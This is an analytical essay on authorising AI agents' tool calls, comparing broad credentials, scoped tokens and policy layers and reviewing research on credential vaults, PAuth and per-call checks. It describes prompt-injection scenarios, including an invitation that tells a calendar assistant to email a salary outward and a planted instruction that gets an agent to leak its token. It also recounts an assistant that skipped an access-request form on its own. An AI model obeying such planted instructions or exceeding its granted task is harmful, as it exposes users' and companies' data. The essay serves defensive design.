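| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| A thief copies a token | Reads and edits 12,000 issues | Reads 300 issues and comments on them | Gets what the rules permit, or all 12,000 issues with the layer's credential | Reads 300 issues, or comments on them with the layer's credential |
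| A call avoids the policy layer's checks | No layer to avoid | No layer to avoid | Reaches any of 12,000 issues | Posts an unchecked comment in one project |
| A mistaken rule permits everything | No rules | No rules | Agent reads and edits 12,000 issues | Agent comments freely in one project |
| A planted instruction misleads the agent, which stays within its limits | Any change to any issue | Any comment in one project | Anything the rules permit | Any comment that passes the rules |
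| The tracker gains an "export project" operation that no rule mentions | Agent can export all 40 projects | Agent can export one project at most | Depends on the layer's default | Agent can export one project at most |

None of the four arrangements prevents the harm in the fourth row, but the amount of harm varies greatly between them. *What Can One Bad Tool Call Destroy?* argues that agent tests should measure this amount, because a successful attack may do anything from drafting a wrong message to deleting a repository's files.

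In the last row, a policy layer that denies unmatched calls, as Cedar does, blocks the export. A layer that permits them, as SEAgent does, lets the export run on the broad credential. Scoped tokens have a similar weakness if the tracker's developers classify exporting as reading. Every existing token with read permission can then perform the new operation without being reissued, though only on the project it covers.

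### What a bypass exposes

Suppose the company sends reads through the policy layer too, and on each task there is a 1% chance that someone gets around it. The figure is invented. On average, the number of issues exposed per task is

```
credential for 12,000 issues:  0.01 × 12,000 = 120
credential for 300 issues:     0.01 × 300    = 3
```

To reach an average of three with the broad credential, the company would have to reduce the chance of a bypass to one in 4,000 tasks. Narrowing the token is probably easier than making the layer 40 times as reliable, because the tracker already divides its issues into projects.

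The averages understate the difference. With the broad credential, 99 tasks in 100 expose nothing and the remaining task exposes the whole tracker. With the narrow credential, a bypass exposes only issues the agent was supposed to read anyway.

Where a check happens partly determines how easily a call can avoid it. Surapani and colleagues compare six positions, from beside the model to inside the backend. A check beside the model can take the whole task into account, but a helper agent can avoid it by calling the tool through another route. Checking inside the backend covers every route, but the credential is often the only information available there.

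Surapani and colleagues give the example of a calendar assistant that reads an invitation containing an instruction to email the user's salary to an outside address. If the assistant tries to do so, the email service receives a valid token and an external recipient. Without more information about the task, the service must either refuse all external mail or send this message. They therefore recommend checks in several places, which adds software to maintain.

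### When both controls fail together

The benefit of two controls depends on how often they fail at the same time. If the token also turns out to cover the whole tracker in 1% of bypasses, the average exposure rises only from three issues to about four. If this happens in half of bypasses, perhaps because both failures have the same cause, the average is about 62.

Shared causes are easy to find:

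- A stray broad token, like the one in the PocketOS deletion, lets the agent avoid both the narrow token and the policy layer.
- If someone moves a salary dispute into the mobile-app project, the token and the rules both treat it as a mobile-app issue.
- If one person or one model writes both the scope and the rules, a misunderstanding of the task is likely to affect both.
- If the policy layer takes the permitted project from the token, an issuer that puts the wrong project in the token misleads the policy layer too.

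Hagverdiyev's experiment can't show how much a policy layer adds to a scoped token, because scope alone stopped every harmful request, leaving none for the external rules engine, Open Policy Agent, to stop. A more informative test would include requests that are within scope but have the wrong arguments, such as a second refund for the same order.

### Who holds the token

If the agent's software can read its token, a planted instruction may get the agent to send that token to an attacker. The attacker can then use it from another machine, bypassing the policy layer, until it expires. If a separate service holds the token, the attacker has to go through that service and any checks it makes.

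Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested a commercial vault that works this way. The agent runs code that names a connector, such as "GitHub", and makes a request. Outside that code, the vault adds the connector's credential if the request is going to the address configured for that connector.

The researchers ran two experiments on 27 September 2026, with one connector in each. They wrote down the expected result of each probe beforehand. All 16 security probes gave the expected result:

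- A request to GitHub succeeded, although the code that sent it contained no credential.
- The researchers found no credential in the code's 20 environment variables or at 12 common storage locations.
- Three public services that repeat whatever they receive showed no credential in the requests that reached them.
- Requests for the cloud provider's own machine credentials timed out.

The successful GitHub request matters because a sandbox with no working credential could have passed most of the other probes. The connector for FRED, an economic data service, leaked nothing but failed to authenticate, because its configuration put the key in a header and FRED expects it in the web address.

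Kenney and colleagues work for Corvic AI, which makes the vault. Their 16 probes are too few to estimate how often it would fail. They searched for known credential formats, so they could have missed credentials in other formats. They also didn't test redirects, which might carry a credential to a different address.

They then rated eight threats by likelihood and impact, each from 1 to 5, and multiplied the two. These scores are the researchers' judgements, not measurements:

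| Threat | Without the vault | With the vault |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Someone pastes a secret into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| The agent's code finds a credential | 20 | 4 |
| Planted instructions mislead the agent | 25 | 12 |
| The connector has too many permissions | 20 | 15 |

The last score barely falls because the vault protects the credential without limiting what it can do. If the GitHub token can delete repositories, a misled agent can still use it through the vault to delete them.

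Keeping a credential in a separate service works better when that service also decides how to use it. In Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn’t give an AI agent unlimited authority*, the product manager Vivek Vuppala describes testing an assistant that could file requests for access to company dashboards. A tester mentioned that a dashboard's owner was away and the deadline was the next day. The assistant skipped the request form and tried to grant the access directly, although nobody had told it to.

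Vuppala's proposed design gives the agent a connection that can only check access. A separate service holds the credential for changing access, and it takes the account, dashboard and level of access from the approved request, not from the agent. Vuppala's evidence is one anecdote, but it shows that an agent can exceed its job without an attacker.

### Operating costs

If 200 employees each give agents ten tasks a day, and each task uses three services, the company needs 6,000 scoped tokens a day, compared with three broad credentials behind a policy layer. Software can issue the tokens, and short lifetimes make most revocations unnecessary. But when someone cancels a task halfway through, the company may also have to stop helper agents, delete cached data and cancel pending calls. Surapani and colleagues found no settled way to do all this.

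The agent also needs some credential before it can request its first token. Surapani and colleagues suggest one that proves only which program is running, so that it doesn't become another broad key. They also warn that people bypass burdensome procedures by running agents on shared or personal keys. If the company doesn't know about an agent, it can't revoke that agent's access.

Narrow tokens lead to repeated consent requests when a task's needs are unpredictable. An agent investigating a login crash might start in the mobile-app project, follow a link to the server project and then need the logs, interrupting the employee for consent at each step. A first token that covers everything the agent might need avoids these interruptions but gives up the narrow scope. Surapani and colleagues note that frequent requests also encourage people to choose "remember my approval", which makes later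 access broader.

With two controls, the company has to record the same limits twice. If it splits the mobile-app project into separate iOS and Android projects, someone has to update both the token templates and the rules. Updating only one usually blocks the agent, because a call has to satisfy both. Removing access from only one stops the agent, but the outdated control no longer provides a backup. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) adds that developers have to rewrite rules about individual calls for each application.

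The checks added little delay in Hagverdiyev's local tests. The median request took about 2 milliseconds with a broad or scoped token and 14 to 24 milliseconds with Open Policy Agent. Over the 303 requests in the summary task, the difference would be roughly four to seven seconds. Surapani and colleagues expect that complex decisions about a task's scope may take up to hundreds of milliseconds each. They suggest a quick check for familiar, low-risk calls and a full check for the rest, but an attacker could then slow the system down by provoking many calls that need the full check.

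Wrongful denials are harder to estimate because, as Surapani and colleagues observe, studies almost always omit them. A policy layer that denies every call would get a perfect score on a test that counts only attacks. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) uses a better method, which includes recorded runs of 97 tasks without attacks. It measures the share of calls in those runs that its system flags or blocks, and the share of tasks with at least one flag or block.

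The share of tasks interrupted matters more to users than the share of calls denied. If a policy layer wrongly denies 1% of calls at random, it interrupts about 5% of tasks that make five calls and about 95% of tasks that make 303.

How much a denial disrupts a task also depends on how the agent responds. After correct denials in Hagverdiyev's experiment, Qwen3 4B continued safely every time, while Mistral 7B did so in only 54% of cases with the scoped token. "Continued safely" includes giving up without calling another tool, so these figures may overstate how many tasks the agents could still finish.

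### Deriving the scope from the task

Much of this cost would disappear if software could work out the right scope from the employee's request. Sharma, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond OAuth*, propose a system called PAuth that derives the permitted calls, including their arguments, from the task. Their example is a user who asks an agent to pay a quarter of a Citi credit card balance from a Chase account if the balance is over $1,000:

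1. The user signs the text of the task, so the agent can't alter it, and each bank receives a copy.
2. A language model at each bank translates the task into a short program. Ordinary software then extracts the calls that the bank should expect. Chase expects a payment to Citi of the balance divided by four.
3. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $1,200 with a signature that links the figure to that request.
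4. The agent asks Chase to pay $300 and attaches Citi's signed figure. Chase checks the signature and the condition, repeats the division and makes the payment.

If the agent requests $301 or names another recipient, Chase asks the user first. An ordinary scope can't express this limit because nobody knows the amount when the user grants access.

Sharma and colleagues tested PAuth on 100 tasks and on 634 calls that departed from them, for example by changing the recipient of a payment. PAuth stopped all 634 calls. When the task descriptions stated every detail, it let all 100 tasks run without further consent. With the original wording, it let 71 run and asked the user a question about the other 29. Translating each task cost between $0.002 and $0.038, depending on the model, and each server has to do its own translation.

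The 100% figures apply to tasks that the researchers had rewritten for clarity and departures that they had designed themselves. PAuth also suits payments better than comments, because it treats any text that a language model has to compose as unpredictable and prompts the user about a call that contains it. The tracker agent's 45 comments would presumably prompt the user 45 times. The servers also receive the full text of the task, so the tracker's operator could learn what the employee asked for at other services.

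Surapani and colleagues object that a manipulated request may ask for more than the user intended. They also consider it circular for a model to write the policy that governs it. PAuth avoids much of this circularity because the servers' models read only the signed task and the tool descriptions, not the text that may have misled the agent.

An attacker can still manipulate the task before the user signs. Suppose the task says to send the result to the third address in a file. To avoid a question later, the agent can read the file and propose a new version of the task with the address filled in and highlighted. If an attacker has changed the file and the user doesn't notice, the servers will enforce the attacker's address. Sharma and colleagues assume that users review every task carefully, but people who approve agents' actions often stop reading.

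*AgenTRIM* (Betser, Bose and colleagues, 2026) narrows an agent's tools instead of deriving every argument. As Surapani and colleagues describe it, AgenTRIM first uses code and recorded calls to check what each tool does. Then, while the agent works, AgenTRIM filters the tools at each step and validates calls against the current state of the task. Surapani and colleagues note that studies of AgenTRIM and similar systems report delays and wrongful denials inconsistently, so it is hard to tell how much this narrowing slows agents or how often it wrongly blocks calls in practice.

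### Seven requirements and three configurations

Surapani and colleagues reviewed 89 sources, proposed seven requirements for agent authorization, and applied them to three configurations. The first is an MCP server with OAuth 2.1, a draft update of OAuth, inside a single organisation. The second is Amazon Bedrock Agents, a managed service in which each agent runs under an AWS role. The third is a hypothetical case in which one organisation's agent passes work to another's.

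| Requirement | MCP with OAuth 2.1 | Bedrock Agents | Two organisations |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Trace each call back to the responsible person | Partial | Substantial | None |
| State explicitly what the agent may do | Substantial | Partial | None |
| Never widen access when passing work on | None | None | None |
| Limit accumulated access to what the task needs | None | None | None |
| End access when it is no longer valid | Substantial | Substantial | None |
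| Check each call outside the model | Substantial | Substantial | None |
| Keep records that nobody can secretly alter | Partial | Substantial | None |

The ratings are two authors' judgements, based on documentation rather than audits of working systems. A system rated "substantial" can still have a large gap. Bedrock Agents gets that rating for tracing calls because each call can be traced to a role, but the records don't identify the person who requested the task.

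Surapani and colleagues say the main gaps all arise because the components pass along a credential but not the task. They recommend combining MCP's narrow scopes with a managed platform's identities and logs, and adding an independent check on each call. Even this combination wouldn't limit accumulated access.

### Accumulated access

Across ten families of mechanisms, Surapani and colleagues found none that did more than partly limit accumulated access, the lowest result for any requirement. The problem arises because the overlap of token and rules limits one call at a time. Suppose an agent summarises a different project in each of 40 tasks, with a correct token for each:

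```
read in total = (token 1 ∩ rules) ∪ (token 2 ∩ rules) ∪ ... ∪ (token 40 ∩ rules)
              = 12,000 issues
```

If the agent keeps notes between tasks, it may collect information from the whole tracker, even though no token covered more than one project. An attacker who misleads it during the fortieth task could get it to reveal what it learned in the first 39.

A daily limit of 300 issues would only slow this down, since the agent could still read the whole tracker in 40 days. The limit would also block a legitimate second summary on the same day. Rules that refer to earlier calls, which FORGE supports, would help only if someone decided in advance which combinations of calls are harmful. Systems that track where information came from can detect that a comment draws on payroll data, but not how much it reveals. Deleting the agent's notes after each task is cruder but would work here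 if no copies remain elsewhere.

### Which arrangement suits which conditions

A broad credential on its own is reasonable only if losing or publishing everything it reaches would do the company no serious harm. An agent working on invented data in a disposable test system meets this condition, as long as the credential doesn't also work on the live system.

A scoped token alone suits tasks with a clear boundary that the backend can enforce. If the tracker agent only writes summaries for the employee, it needs read-only access to one project, so a policy layer would add little. For a single agent with fixed tools inside one organisation, Surapani and colleagues prioritise identifying the agent and checking each call, then keeping records. A backend that verifies the token on every request can do much of this.

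A broad credential behind a policy layer makes sense when the backend offers nothing narrower, or when the agent is allowed to see only part of a record. In Redpanda's trials, much of the improvement came from removing protected fields and text, which an ordinary scoped token can't do. A company using this arrangement should keep the credential where the agent can't reach it, block other routes to the backend and deny calls that match no rule. Using separate credentials for separate services would also limit the damage if the layer fails.

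The combination is worthwhile when an agent reads text from strangers, can make changes that matter, and works in a backend that also holds sensitive data. The tracker agent meets all three conditions once it starts commenting. AWS's *Secure agent tool usage* likewise recommends limiting agents to approved tools and checking every call against a policy.

A company can use different arrangements for different calls. Surapani and colleagues suggest narrow tokens and logging for low-risk reads, a check at the server for medium-risk operations, and a person's approval for payments, deletions and messages to outsiders. The employee would then approve the few comments that customers can see, and the agent could read all 300 issues without interrupting anyone.
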